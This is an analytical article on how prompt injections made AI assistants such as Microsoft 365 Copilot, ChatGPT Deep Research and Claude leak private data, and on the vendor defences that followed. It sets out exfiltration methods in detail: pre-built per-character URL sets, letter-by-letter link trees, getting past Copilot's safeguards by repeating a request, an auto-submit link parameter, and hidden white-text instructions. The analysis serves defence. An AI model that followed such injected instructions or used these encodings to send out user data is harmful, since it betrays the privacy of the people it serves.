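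### SearchLeak and ReLeak: Bing forwards the data

The list Aim published in 2025 included bing.com and its subdomains. A year later, the security company Varonis found that Bing also had a service that would fetch an outside address. Its *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot's search function that combined three flaws and needed one click from the victim.

The victim clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft address that also contained instructions for Copilot. Copilot ran them as if the user had typed them and searched for private data. The next flaw was a race condition, a fault whose effect depends on which of two operations finishes first. It let the attacker insert HTML, the code browsers use to build web pages, into the page. That HTML included an image on bing.com, which the policy permitted, and Bing's servers then fetched the attacker's address (Taler, 2026,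 *SearchLeak*). This is usually called server-side request forgery, which means getting a server to make a request that the attacker has chosen.

SearchLeak could expose emails, including one-time login codes, as well as meeting details and company files. The Next Web reports that Microsoft registered the flaw as CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June 2026 and rated it critical, although it scored only 6.5 on the standard severity scale. It adds that anti-phishing tools were unlikely to flag the link because it led to microsoft.com. An attacker could therefore exploit trust in a whole domain both in those tools and in Copilot's page.

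Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025, and Aim's researchers moved there. On 3 December 2026, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) announced that the team had found three more zero-click ways to take data from Microsoft 365 Copilot. Each began like EchoLeak, with an email that Copilot came across while answering an ordinary question. The team had reported them to Microsoft between 29 July and 20 August.

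One of the three used Bing again. Copilot wrote private data into an image's address, the browser loaded the image, and Bing passed the data to an outside server. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, a report on a Russian security news site, likens this route to the one in SearchLeak, except that the user no longer had to click. So despite any changes Microsoft had made after Varonis's report, Bing could still forward data from Copilot's page at least six weeks after Varonis published. Microsoft may have concentrated on the link and the race condition, which let the attacker in, and only partly blocked the route that let data out. Microsoft fixed this version, CVE-2026-124115, on 15 November.

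That history is the strongest evidence against relying on Copilot's list as it stood. Aim had shown in 2025 that an attacker could use a listed Microsoft domain to fetch web addresses, and Bing was on the same published list. A review of the other entries for similar services could have found the problem before Varonis did, though it would have been slow. Ravia calls Aim's search through the permitted domains "nitpicky" and describes some of it as tedious.

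Such searches are becoming easier. Antipov reports that Cato's researchers directed AI agents that wrote test cases, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. If attackers can do the same, they are more likely to find an obscure forwarding page on a large domain.

### ReLeak's other routes avoided the browser

The second ReLeak attack, CVE-2026-124132, used Copilot's ability to create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files. Copilot saved a document with a link that contained private data. Microsoft's servers process new files in OneDrive and SharePoint in the background, and they contacted the link's address while processing the document. In Cato's tests, the data left between one and eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if the employee never opened the document.

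No rule for the chat page could have prevented this, because the employee's browser was not involved in sending the data. The employee would also have been less likely to notice than with an image, because nothing had to appear in the answer. Microsoft fixed the flaw on 11 November.

The third attack, CVE-2026-78501, got data out of Copilot's code interpreter, which runs short Python programs for tasks such as calculations. The programs run in an isolated sandbox. According to Microsoft's documentation, no network traffic can enter or leave it, which is stricter than any allowlist because no destinations are permitted. Cato's researchers still broke through the isolation and sent data directly to an outside server. The flaw's severity score rose from 7.4 to 8.6 on review, and Microsoft fixed this flaw first, on 17 September. Companies can add the same interpreter to agents built with Microsoft's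 Agent Builder and Copilot Studio, but Antipov notes that nobody has confirmed whether those agents had the flaw.

Cato knew of no one who had used ReLeak to steal customers' data. According to *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026), Microsoft made all three fixes on its own servers and told customers they didn't need to do anything. That is convenient for customers, but it gives them little to inspect if they want to know what Copilot can now contact.

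### Microsoft's layers of defence

In its 2025 account of its defenses against prompt injection, Microsoft says it marks outside text and runs classifiers. Because some injections will get through, it also limits the damage with data permissions, requests for user consent and deterministic blocks on known ways of sending data out. Copilot's link filter and image policy are blocks of this kind.

EchoLeak defeated both the classifiers and the blocks, and Faisal reports that Microsoft's protections against injection stopped none of the three ReLeak attacks. Cato concludes that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato sells security products for AI, and its researchers set out to find failures, so their results don't show how many attacks the defences stop. Still, their conclusion is hard to dismiss, because the same team succeeded against the same product twice in two years.

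The hole in the image policy is easier to close permanently than the one in the classifiers, because once Microsoft restricts the fetching service in Teams, no rewording of the email can reopen that route. A deterministic block is therefore still worth having after someone has found a hole in it. However, Microsoft describes its block as covering "known" methods, so it won't stop leaks through another forwarding service until somebody reports that service.

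### Trusting a domain as a whole

Except for the one that Salesforce let expire, every domain in these cases belonged to the company the product team thought owned it. But a domain allowlist treats all pages on a domain alike. Most pages on docs.google.com or bing.com only show something to the visitor, though a few store what they receive or pass it on. GitHub's image proxy passed data on by design.

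The people who write a list of trusted domains often have no control over the pages on those domains. An engineer who adds link previews to Teams has little reason to know that a Copilot page is allowed to load images from Teams. A domain that was harmless when a team approved it can therefore become dangerous after a routine update to another product. Wildcards make this worse because they also allow addresses that don't exist yet.

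A team can narrow the entries in a Content Security Policy by listing a folder, such as office.example/icons, instead of a whole site. This would have blocked a fetching service elsewhere on the same domain, but pictures stop loading if another team moves them out of the folder. W3C also designed the policy so that the browser checks only the domain after a redirect, because otherwise a website could use the policy to learn where another site had sent the visitor. An open redirect on one listed domain can therefore still lead to any page on another listed domain.

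Keeping images on a separate domain that only serves files is safer. Such a domain has no forms or fetching service that could pass a request on, and the attacker can't read its logs. Several entries on Copilot's list, such as those for connector icons, appear to work this way already. A company can move icons and logos to such a domain without users noticing. The charts and slides that Copilot has shown in its answers since July 2026 are harder to move, because they come from customers' own files, which many customers keep in SharePoint.

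## Web pages the assistant may open

A Content Security Policy usually has no effect when an assistant opens a web page itself, because the request comes from the AI company's servers, not the user's browser. Web pages are also harder to restrict than pictures. Microsoft can host its own icons, but an assistant that opened only its maker's pages would be of little use for research.

OpenAI and Anthropic restrict individual addresses instead of relying only on lists of domains. Whether the assistant may open an address depends on its source, which could be the user, a search engine, a stranger's email or the model itself. Both companies tightened their rules after researchers found a permitted source that an attacker could control.

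### ShadowLeak: the agent adds data to an address

ChatGPT's Deep Research mode spends five to 30 minutes reading web pages and documents, then writes a report. A user can also connect it to a Gmail account. In June 2025 the security company Radware told OpenAI that a single email could make Deep Research send out private data from the mailbox without the user seeing anything.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes a user who asks OpenAI's Deep Research agent to go through the day's emails about a new employee. One email contains the employee's name and home address. Another, from an attacker, presents a website as a staff directory and asks the agent to look the employee up there. The agent puts the name and address into the URL and opens it, and the attacker reads both in the site's log. The employer's security tools can't intercept the request, because it goes from OpenAI's servers to the attacker's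 without passing through the employer's network.

This is the email about restructuring documents that OpenAI later published as an example of a persuasive injection. OpenAI reports that it worked half the time, while Radware reports that it worked 100% of the time. Radware sent OpenAI a more reliable version a day after its first report, so the two figures may describe different versions.

ChatGPT had some defences. The model refused Radware's first attempts, and once it searched the web for the suspicious address instead of opening it. Even when it did try to open the address, some requests failed, and it left out the personal details until the researchers got it to encode them. These defences seem to have relied on the model or some other software detecting a problem. Radware found no fixed limit on the sites the agent could open. OpenAI's url_safe check covered images, but Radware saw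 nothing comparable for the agent's own browsing.

OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August without telling Radware and marked it as resolved on 3 September. Afterwards, ChatGPT opened web addresses only in the exact form it had received them and would not add anything to them, even when told to. Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* presents this rule as OpenAI's response to ShadowLeak. Embrace The Red dates the stricter image checks to about the same month, so OpenAI may have changed both together.

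The rule was an improvement because it didn't depend on recognising personal data. If the assistant can't alter the address pictures.example/sun.png, it can't add Ana's email address to it, encoded or not. It is unclear from the outside whether ordinary software enforced the rule or OpenAI had trained the model to refuse. The next attack would have worked either way, because it didn't alter any addresses.

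### ZombieAgent: the attacker prepares the addresses

On 26 September 2025, about three weeks after OpenAI closed the first case, Radware's Zvika Babo reported a way around the new rule. His email, described in Radware's *ZombieAgent*, contained a ready-made web address for each letter and digit, plus one for a space. ChatGPT found the private text in the mailbox and opened the addresses in the order that spelled it. Rehberger and Mayraz had done the same with images.

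Requests can arrive out of order, which had troubled Rehberger in 2023. Babo also dealt with this problem, preparing a separate set of addresses for each position in the text, so that an "a" in first place had a different address from an "a" in second place. A text of ten letters and digits then needs 360 addresses. This takes the attacker almost no effort, because one small program can answer requests for all of them.

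Sending text one character at a time is slow, but some valuable data is short. In another demonstration, ChatGPT sent email addresses from the victim's inbox to Radware's server, which automatically sent the same malicious email to each one. An email address is often only about 20 characters long, and a few are enough to spread the attack through an organisation.

A press report, *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, blames OpenAI for not restricting ChatGPT from adding a single letter to a web address. According to Babo, ChatGPT added nothing, because the email already contained every address in full. If so, a stricter ban on changing addresses would not have helped, and OpenAI had to restrict who could supply them.

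It did so on 16 December 2025. According to the press report, ChatGPT would no longer open a link from an email unless the link appeared in a well-known public index or the user had provided it in the chat. OpenAI published a fuller account of this approach six weeks later.

### OpenAI's index of public addresses

The design that OpenAI described on 28 January 2026 depends on a crawler, a program that moves from page to page across the public web and records the addresses it finds. The crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts. The check works as follows:

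1. An agent is about to open a page or load an image automatically.
2. OpenAI's software looks for the exact address in the crawler's index.
3. If the address is there, the agent opens it without asking.
4. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning.
5. The warning explains that OpenAI hasn't verified the link and that it may include information from the conversation. The user can then decide whether to open it.

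In Ana's case, the index might well contain pictures.example/sun.png. It would not contain that URL with her email address added after a question mark, because nobody had published that version before her assistant wrote it. The crawler has no access to her conversation, so a URL it has recorded can contain her private data only if the data was already public or somebody guessed it.

OpenAI considered a list of reputable sites and found two problems. One was that checking only the first domain misses redirects. The index would stop an attacker from sending Ana's data through a trusted site that forwards visitors, because the whole address has to match one in the index, including the part that names the destination. An open redirect the crawler has already recorded can lead only to a destination somebody chose beforehand, without Ana's data in it.

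A strict list also leaves out so many sites that people would see frequent false warnings and learn to dismiss them. An index of individual addresses can cover obscure sites without anyone vouching for their owners, so ordinary reading should trigger fewer warnings. OpenAI's announcement includes no figures on the number of warnings.

Rehberger observes that the index is still an allowlist, but it is much longer and more precise than one a team could write by hand. It would have blocked the leaks that got past domain lists by using a newly composed address. For example, Superhuman's policy allowed every address on docs.google.com, including one that would fill in a form with the text of Ana's emails. That address would not be in an index of public pages.

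OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak user-specific data through the URL itself. A user who dismisses the warning can still send the data. OpenAI also doesn't promise that a page is truthful or free of malicious instructions.

Choosing between permitted addresses can also leak data. According to Rehberger, OpenAI acknowledges this in the accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. An attacker needs 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit, and Rehberger points out that a larger blog probably has them already. The index therefore blocks addresses that an attacker has just invented for an email, as Babo did, but not pages that the attacker published earlier and the crawler has found.

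### Where the check applies

In March 2026 OpenAI named the mechanism Safe Url and described it more broadly. It detects when information the assistant learned in a conversation would go to a third party. OpenAI then either blocks the transmission and tells the agent to find another way, or shows the user the information and asks for confirmation. In the second case, Ana could notice her own email address in the information shown.

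Safe Url covers the pages the agent visits and the bookmarks it makes in Atlas, OpenAI's web browser. In Deep Research it covers page visits and also searches, whose terms can contain private data too. ChatGPT's Canvas and Apps features, which let the assistant create and run small applications, use a similar approach. Those applications run in a sandbox that detects unexpected communications and asks for the user's consent.

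This list partly addresses Rehberger's worry that some OpenAI developers might not know about the protection. However, it doesn't show that every version of each product makes the check, and the earlier image check was missing from the phone app.

OpenAI says most attacks of this type fail because its safety training makes the agent refuse, so Safe Url rarely has to act. In *The Framing Gap* (2026), outside researchers tried to extract a secret through ChatGPT and failed in all 48 valid trials, which is consistent with the product being well protected. The same attacks succeeded up to 100% of the time against the model through its application programming interface (API), which lets developers build a model into their own software.

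Forty-eight failed attempts don't rule out a true success rate of up to about 6%, which would be high for a product with over a billion users. The researchers couldn't inspect ChatGPT's internal workings and don't attribute its resistance to any particular defence. Still, the contrast suggests that developers who use OpenAI's model shouldn't assume they also get ChatGPT's protection.

The researchers also tried instructing the model to protect the secret. A policy against revealing it "in any form" cut leaks from 31.9% to zero, but with a policy that named specific behaviours and omitted that phrase, the rate was 48.8%. A rule about which addresses the assistant may open doesn't depend on how the model's instructions are worded.

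### How much a choice of pages reveals

If an assistant may open any one of N addresses, and the attacker can see which one it opened, the remaining leak is at most log₂ N bits per request. A bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question, so a choice between two pages can reveal one answer, a choice among four can reveal two, and each further doubling adds one more.

A text of ten letters and digits has 36¹⁰ possible values, so it contains at most about 51.7 bits (10 × log₂ 36). The smallest number of requests that can always send it is that figure divided by log₂ N, rounded up.

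| Addresses the assistant may choose from | Most bits per request | Requests for ten characters |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 52 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 10 |
| 4,096 | 12 | 5 |
| 1,048,576 | 20 | 3 |

With 4,096 addresses, the attacker can use a separate page for every pair of characters, since there are 1,296 pairs. A ten-character name takes five requests. The attacker would have to explain this code to the model in the injected instructions.

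Increasing an attacker's pages from 36 to 4,096, more than a hundredfold, only halves the number of requests needed to leak the same data. Limiting requests is much more effective than limiting pages, because the leak shrinks in direct proportion to the number of requests. A company that can't limit how many pages an attacker owns could still limit how many pages from one unfamiliar site the assistant opens in a conversation.

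Banning addresses that the model composes also slows the leak. Anthropic's tool for opening pages accepts addresses of up to 250 characters. If a model could write most of such an address itself, using a 64-symbol encoding, it could send well over 1,000 bits in one request. Choosing one of 36 pages sends about 5 bits, so the same data would take more than 200 requests, which a user or a monitoring system is more likely to notice.

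A low rate doesn't protect short secrets. Whether a company plans to close a factory is one bit, and one request can reveal it. A random 20-character password made of capital letters, small letters and digits contains about 119 bits, which ten requests can reveal if each one chooses among 4,096 pages. These figures assume that the model follows the code correctly and that the attacker can reconstruct the order of the requests, so a real attack may need more requests.

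### Claude may not compose an address

In September 2025, Anthropic added web_fetch, a tool that retrieves the text of a web page or PDF, to the Claude API. From the start, Anthropic limited which addresses the tool could open. Willison (2025) reported in *Claude API* that it could open addresses from the user's messages, earlier searches, pages it had already fetched, and the results of tools that ran in the developer's own software, but not addresses that Claude had composed.

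Willison tested Anthropic's consumer app and found the same restriction. This deterministic control would block an injected instruction to add Ana's email address to a URL and open it, because the software would not find the resulting URL in a permitted source.

Anthropic's rule doesn't require an index of the web, and it lets a user share a page created a minute ago. But an address counts as safe once it has appeared in the conversation, and an attacker may have put it there. Willison noticed that developers often paste outside text, such as a customer's email, into a message that the API treats as the user's. The links in the email then count as the user's own. He still thought the ban on addresses composed by the assistant gave the most protection against common attacks.

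In its *Web fetch tool* documentation as of June 2026, Anthropic warned that the rule left a "residual risk" and told developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that wasn't sensitive. Developers worried about leaks could turn the tool off, limit it to certain domains or cap the number of requests, which was unlimited by default.

### The Memory Heist: following links letter by letter

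Claude's consumer app can remember facts from past conversations, which gives an attacker private data to steal even if the user hasn't connected a mailbox. On 9 July 2026, Ayush Paul published an attack on the app called *The Memory Heist*. He had built a website for a fake coffee shop, with instructions for Claude to find the user's profile by following links, one letter at a time.

Each page offered 27 links, one for each letter of the alphabet and one for a hyphen. When Claude chose a letter, the site produced a new page with 27 longer addresses, and so on until the path spelled the user's name. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) explains that the site showed its instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude. A user who checked the page in an ordinary browser would not have seen them.

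Every address came from a page that web_fetch had just retrieved, and Claude composed none of them, so the rule permitted each one. Paul obtained the user's name, employer and home city. In *The Read-Only Lie*, the blogger dyb calculates that each choice among 27 links revealed 4.75 bits and that the whole attack took about 30 requests, which revealed roughly 143 bits in total.

Paul had never told Claude his home city, but Claude inferred it from the name of a hackathon he had attended in high school. Someone who reviews the assistant's memory for obvious secrets could therefore miss facts that an attacker can still obtain.

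Twenty-seven symbols allow about 206 trillion possible ten-character paths, but Paul's site had to create only 27 new links at each step. An index like OpenAI's would have been a better defence here, because no crawler could have recorded more than a tiny fraction of those pages in advance.

Anthropic responded by stopping web_fetch from opening links found on fetched pages. It declined to pay Paul a reward, saying it had already identified the problem internally. The weakness had also been visible since launch in Anthropic's published rule, which listed earlier fetch results as a permitted source of links. Anthropic probably allowed these links because many tasks require following them, such as reading a manual with one page per chapter.

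dyb proposes a less restrictive fix, letting Claude follow links only on sites the user has named in that conversation. A user could then open the manual's contents page and have Claude read the chapters. This would protect someone whose assistant reached a malicious site through a search, but not someone who asked about the coffee shop by giving its web address, and people do ask assistants about unfamiliar businesses.

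Another proposal is to detect the attack's pattern, in which each address was one character longer than the last. Such a detector would need few resources, and dyb suggests combining it with other signals to avoid flagging ordinary browsing. But an attacker could evade it by assigning whole words to pages or changing the site's layout. Blocking links on fetched pages prevents the attack more reliably, but it also restricts useful browsing.

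### The developer tools still follow links

Anthropic didn't make the same change the default for developers. According to its current API documentation, an assistant can still open addresses from earlier web_fetch results, so it can follow links on a page it has fetched. Developers can exclude these addresses with a setting called url_sources.

The documentation also describes a gap in the ban on composed addresses. If a developer gives Claude a tool that runs programs on the developer's own computer and returns their output, Claude can write a program that prints a new address. That address then counts as a tool result, which web_fetch may open by default. This could be worse than the Memory Heist, because the address could contain a whole secret instead of a single letter. Anthropic explains how to exclude such a tool with url_sources but leaves it to the developer to do so.

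The API now also blocks an address if it seems to contain a password or an access key, unless the developer's instructions or the user's message included that credential. This should catch some crude leaks, but the check has to recognise the credential, so it would miss one that an agent split across 20 requests.

Anthropic chose a different combination of rules for Managed Agents, a service that runs agents for developers. The *Claude Platform release notes* (2026) record that from 7 October the service's web_fetch tool opened only addresses that had already appeared in the session, to reduce the risk of data exfiltration. The tool can't open addresses that appear only in attached documents or in the output of other tools, which closes the gap with printed addresses. It can still open links on pages that the agent fetched earlier, although Anthropic had stopped the consumer app from following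 such links three months before.

All of these products let the user supply an address by typing it. They differ in what else they accept:

| Product | Address the model composed | Address in the output of another tool, such as an email search | Link on a page it has opened |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT | Automatically only if indexed | Automatically only if indexed | Automatically only if indexed |
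| Claude app since July 2026 | No | No | No |
| Claude API by default | No, unless a developer's tool repeats it | Yes, if the developer's own software ran the tool | Yes |
| Claude Managed Agents since October 2026 | No | No | Yes |

Anthropic hasn't explained the differences. One plausible reason is that the consumer app stores people's memories, whereas many developers build agents that read only public pages and need to follow links. The looser default is harmless for those agents, but it becomes risky if a developer later adds a connector to private files and doesn't think to revisit a setting for web pages. Blocking links until the developer enables them would be safer, though it would break some existing agents.

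Since 20 October 2026, an organisation's administrators have been able to turn web_fetch off or limit it to chosen domains. In Managed Agents, both the original address and the destination of any redirect must be on the permitted list, so a redirect from an approved site can't lead to an unapproved one.

### Caching and limits on repeat visits

Limiting the agent to indexed pages or banning composed addresses still lets an attacker choose among existing pages. To make that choice less useful, Embrace The Red suggests that the company either keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it if the agent requests the page again, or block the agent from opening the same address twice in a session.

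Both measures disrupt a simple code that uses one page per letter. If the agent tried to send "anna", the attacker's server would log only "an", because the repeated letters would never reach it.

An attacker can use a better code, one that never requires the agent to visit the same page twice. Babo's separate addresses for each position in the text do this, although he designed them to preserve the order. An attacker with only 36 pages could also change what the remaining pages stand for after each request. The first request then offers 36 choices, the next 35, and so on. Ten requests can still reveal about 49.7 bits, compared with 51.7 if the agent may revisit pages.

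Forbidding repeat visits limits the total amount of data the agent can leak. Once it has opened all 36 pages, it has revealed at most about 138 bits, close to what Paul took from Claude. This limit would help against an attacker with one small blog, but not against one with thousands of indexed pages.

Sharing each stored copy among all the company's users would be more effective. After one victim's assistant opened a page, the next victim's assistant would get the stored copy, and the attacker would learn nothing until that copy expired. The attacker would therefore need fresh pages for each victim. With OpenAI's index, the attacker would have to wait for the crawler to find those pages, but a site like Paul's can create new addresses immediately if the assistant is allowed to follow links. OpenAI applies this idea most strictly in Lockdown Mode, which limits browsing to cached content.

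Anthropic already caches the pages that web_fetch retrieves, but its stated reasons are speed and fewer redundant requests. Developers can request a fresh copy instead, and Classmethod's *Claude's Web Fetch tool doesn't necessarily return the latest information* (2026) shows why they might. A developer trying a new feature of Slack, the workplace chat program, got an outdated copy of the documentation through Claude and mistook it for the current version. The cache of a few minutes that Rehberger proposed would rarely cause this mistake, but it would give the attacker a new chance each time the cache expired.

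### What users lose

Under OpenAI's rule, the assistant has trouble with pages missing from the index, such as new or private ones. A crawler may not have found a company announcement published an hour ago. It shouldn't find a family's shared photo album or a customer's parcel-tracking page, because anyone who has the address may be able to open the page. If Ana asks ChatGPT to check the delivery link in her email, ChatGPT may have to show her a warning or leave her to open the link herself.

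The restriction also affects websites that put search terms in their addresses. To compare hotels for a weekend, an agent might normally write an address containing the city, dates and number of guests. That exact combination is unlikely to be in a public index, even though nothing in it came from an attacker. Claude's rule rejects the address because Claude composed it, whether or not it is in an index.

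Users can often get around these limits by typing or pasting an address. Anthropic permits addresses that the user supplies, and as Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT treats them as safe for the rest of the session. Supplying one address takes little effort, but the process becomes tedious when the user wants the assistant to read 15 chapters of a manual, since the Claude app can no longer move from the contents page to the chapters by itself. Claude can still search for each chapter and open the results, but a search engine may not list every chapter.

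When an agent works unattended, no user is there to paste the next address or read a warning. OpenAI's software can direct the agent to try a different website, which keeps the task going but may leave the user with a report based on a second-best source. For an agent that can read a mailbox, that is usually better than letting a stranger's email determine which addresses it opens. An agent with access only to public pages has much less to leak, so banning it from following links mostly makes the research worse.

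## Links that users click, previews, and links that pre-fill a prompt

An assistant that isn't allowed to open an unfamiliar address can still include it in an answer as a link. If the user clicks the link, any private data in the address goes to the site's owner. A Content Security Policy that limits images doesn't prevent this.

Links are harder to give up than images because people need them to check where an answer came from. Some companies have kept links but restricted them. Salesforce's agents can link only to addresses that a customer's administrator has approved, and OpenAI can show a warning before ChatGPT opens an address it hasn't verified.

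More trouble has come from two related conveniences, messaging apps fetching links to preview them and assistants accepting links that pre-fill a prompt.

### Clickable links in Microsoft 365 Copilot

In 2024 Rehberger showed that an email or shared document could make Microsoft 365 Copilot read a user's other messages and put what it found into a link. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* explains that he hid the data with "ASCII smuggling", which uses characters that a computer can read but a screen doesn't display. The link looked ordinary, so even a careful user had little reason to avoid it. Microsoft fixed the problem but didn't disclose how, according to OECD's *Microsoft Copilot Vulnerability Exposed Sensitive Data* (2024).

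A year later, the security researcher Adam Logue found a way to leak data through Mermaid, a notation for writing charts as text. Copilot can use it to draw a flowchart without producing a picture file. Mermaid charts can contain links and their boxes can be restyled, so Logue had Copilot draw one that looked like a login button.

Logue's attack began with an Excel file that contained instructions in white text. When the user asked for a summary, Copilot retrieved the user's recent emails, encoded them and put them in the link address of a button, according to daily.dev's digest of Logue's post. Clicking the button sent the emails to Logue's server.

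Microsoft responded by removing interactive links from Copilot's Mermaid diagrams, though Copilot can still draw them. Cybersecurity News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability* dates the fix to 26 September 2025, six weeks after Logue's report. Users lost little, since few people expect to click on a flowchart. Removing all the links also meant that Microsoft didn't have to decide which ones were dangerous.

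The fix applied only to diagrams. EchoLeak had already got past Copilot's link filter with a second Markdown notation, and Logue found a third place to put a link. A team that restricts links has to do so in every format the page can display, including formats that another team adds later.

Logue's attack was less dangerous than a zero-click one because it needed the user to click. Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* (2025) contrasts it with a version for the code editor Cursor that needed no click. But a click is weak protection when an attacker can choose what the link looks like. People click on login buttons every day, and a button's label doesn't show the address behind it.

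### Messaging apps fetch links for previews

When someone pastes a link into Slack, Discord or Telegram, the app may fetch the page and show its title and a picture below the message. This helps readers decide whether to open the link. It also means that a link that leaks data can do so without a click, because the app requests the address as soon as the message appears.

Suppose Ana talks to her agent through such an app, and a hidden instruction makes the agent reply with a link to pictures.example that ends in her email address. The messaging company's server requests the link to prepare the preview, so her email address appears in the attacker's log before she has read the reply. Restricting which pages the agent may open wouldn't prevent this, since the agent has only sent a message.

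In *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, Willison (2024) described a remedy from Rehberger. Developers whose apps post messages to Slack can turn off link and media previews in those messages. Readers lose the title and thumbnail but can still click the link.

PromptArmor returned to the problem in February 2026, when many people had begun to message AI agents from their phones. Its *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw, a popular agent, leaked data through Telegram with its default settings. Users could stop Telegram from requesting the link's address by adding one line to OpenClaw's configuration file. The fix is easy for someone who knows about it, but people who set up an agent to help with their email have no particular reason to look into link previews.

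PromptArmor also built a website where people could test other combinations of agent and app. The user asks an agent to post a link to the site, which records whether a preview request arrives and what data comes with it. The leak depends on both products, so an agent that is safe in one app can be unsafe in another.

### Copilot Cowork could message its user without asking

Microsoft Copilot Cowork is an agent that works with a company's files, email and Teams chats, using the permissions of the employee who runs it. According to Microsoft's documentation, it asks the employee before taking sensitive actions such as sending an email. But PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (May 2026) reported that Cowork didn't ask when the message was addressed to the employee, and that employees had no setting to change this.

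Data could leak through the exception for messages to oneself, just as it had from chat answers. The messages could contain outside images, which Outlook or Teams loaded when the employee opened them. The case for the exception was that these messages have no outside recipient, and an agent that prepares a weekly review needs some way to deliver it.

PromptArmor hid its instructions in five lines of an 81-line skill, a file that describes how the agent should do a particular task. When the employee asked for a recap of the week's work, Cowork posted a Teams message with images whose addresses contained download links to the employee's recent files. The attack worked in all five trials. Switching to a more capable model, Claude Opus 4.7, exposed more documents because it searched more thoroughly.

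The links were "pre-authenticated", so anyone with the address could download the file without logging in. An attacker could obtain a large spreadsheet with one leaked address rather than many.

An employee would have struggled to notice, because Cowork's record of its actions showed that it had posted to Teams but didn't show the message's contents. Employees can also schedule a task to run every week, in which case nobody is watching.

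PromptArmor considered this a risk of the product's design, not a bug, and published it to warn customers. It describes no fix by Microsoft, only measures that customers can take. Administrators can block downloads from chosen SharePoint sites, which stops Cowork from obtaining the download links. However, this is a major inconvenience for employees, who then can't print those files and have to read them in a browser instead of the Word and Excel apps.

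Microsoft could instead remove outside images from any message that Cowork writes. The agent could still deliver a weekly review without asking for approval, and the employee would perhaps lose a logo. Requiring approval each time would be worse, because a scheduled task would have to wait for someone to return to the computer. Removing images might not be enough by itself, though. PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) warns that recipients' apps may also preview the links in a Teams message.

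### Who should turn previews off

When one company makes the agent and another displays its messages, each can reasonably see the leak as the other's problem. Telegram previews links as its users expect, and OpenClaw only writes a reply. PromptArmor wants messaging apps to offer developers a setting for previews, and wants agent developers to use that setting or pass the choice on to users. It also suggests settings for individual chats, so that a user could keep previews in a family group but turn them off in the chat with an agent.

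The agent's developer seems best placed to choose the default for link previews, because they know that a language model wrote the message and what private data the model could read. A messaging company can't tell whether an automated account is run by an agent with access to a mailbox or by a newspaper whose posts rely on previews. Turning previews off in the agent therefore does less damage than turning them off for every automated account.

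But this relies on every developer knowing about the risk, and PromptArmor still found OpenClaw exposed in Telegram well over a year after Slack's setting became public. Messaging companies could protect more people by leaving previews off for new automated accounts until the developer asks for them. A newspaper that wants previews would only have to change one setting once.

Data can leak even between products made by the same company, as it did between Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, Outlook and Teams. The people who exempted messages to the user may have considered only who would receive them, while those who built Teams presumably expected a person to choose the images.

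### Links that arrive with a prompt

Many assistants accept a prompt as part of a web address. For example, a link to Copilot's website that ends in "?q=Hello" opens Copilot with "Hello" in the text box. People can use such links to share or bookmark a prompt, and some websites have "Summarize with AI" buttons that work in a similar way.

Microsoft has warned that buttons that pre-fill a prompt can be used to manipulate an assistant. In its hypothetical example, a finance chief clicks one on a blog, and weeks later the assistant strongly recommends a particular supplier. Such a link can also cause a leak if the prompt tells the assistant to collect private data and send it somewhere.

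A prompt in a link is harder to defend against than an instruction in an email. Companies try to mark emails and web pages as outside text, but the assistant receives a pre-filled prompt as the user's own request. OpenAI and Anthropic both treat addresses that the user supplied as safe to open, and any address in the prompt might count as one of these.

A product team can have a link fill in the text box and wait for the user to press Enter, or have it submit the prompt as soon as the page loads. Waiting adds one keystroke but gives the user a chance to read the prompt first. Varonis, the company that found SearchLeak, reported attacks on Microsoft and Atlassian assistants that submitted the prompt without waiting.

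### Reprompt and CoSnitch

The first, CVE-2026-24307, affected Copilot Personal, Microsoft's consumer assistant. Varonis calls it Reprompt. Opening a link immediately ran the attacker's prompt under the user's account. Copilot usually refused to open an address without a good reason, so Varonis' researchers presented the task as a puzzle about a picture of a bird. Copilot also removed sensitive data from addresses before opening them, but only on the first attempt. *Reprompt* describes how the researchers got around this by asking Copilot to do everything twice. Copilot deleted their test phrase from the first request and sent it in the second.

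Varonis suspects that Microsoft checked only the first request to save time. The gap made a sensible safeguard almost worthless, because an attacker could get around it just by asking for a repeat.

Once Copilot had contacted the attacker's server, the server could reply with further instructions, each based on what Copilot had already revealed, so inspecting the original link wouldn't show what data the attack would take. According to Ars Technica's *A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot* (2026), the researchers obtained the user's name, location and details of events from past chats, and the attack continued after the user closed the chat.

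Microsoft had fixed Reprompt by the time Varonis published it in January 2026. TechRadar's *Microsoft Copilot AI attack took just a single click to compromise users* describes the patch as blocking prompt injection through URLs. That could mean Microsoft removed pre-filling, stopped submitting pre-filled prompts automatically, or began filtering them.

Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) reports that the "q" value in a Copilot link only filled in the text box, and the user still had to press Enter. But adding a second, undocumented value made Copilot submit the prompt automatically. Microsoft thus seems to have kept pre-filling and tried to stop automatic submission, while leaving a way to turn it back on. It is hard to be sure that this was the Reprompt fix, because Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, before it announced that Microsoft had patched Reprompt.

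The researchers learned about the second value by asking Copilot why a link couldn't submit a prompt, then asking about the details of each answer. One answer eventually included the value and said that Microsoft had disabled it, but it worked when the researchers tried it.

CoSnitch could reach email as well as chat history if the user had connected a Gmail account. The prompt could make Copilot search the inbox, encode what it found and open a web address containing the result. In one test, Copilot retrieved an email containing a password. Varonis also found that a web page could plant instructions in Copilot's permanent memory when the user asked for a summary, so an attack could affect later conversations.

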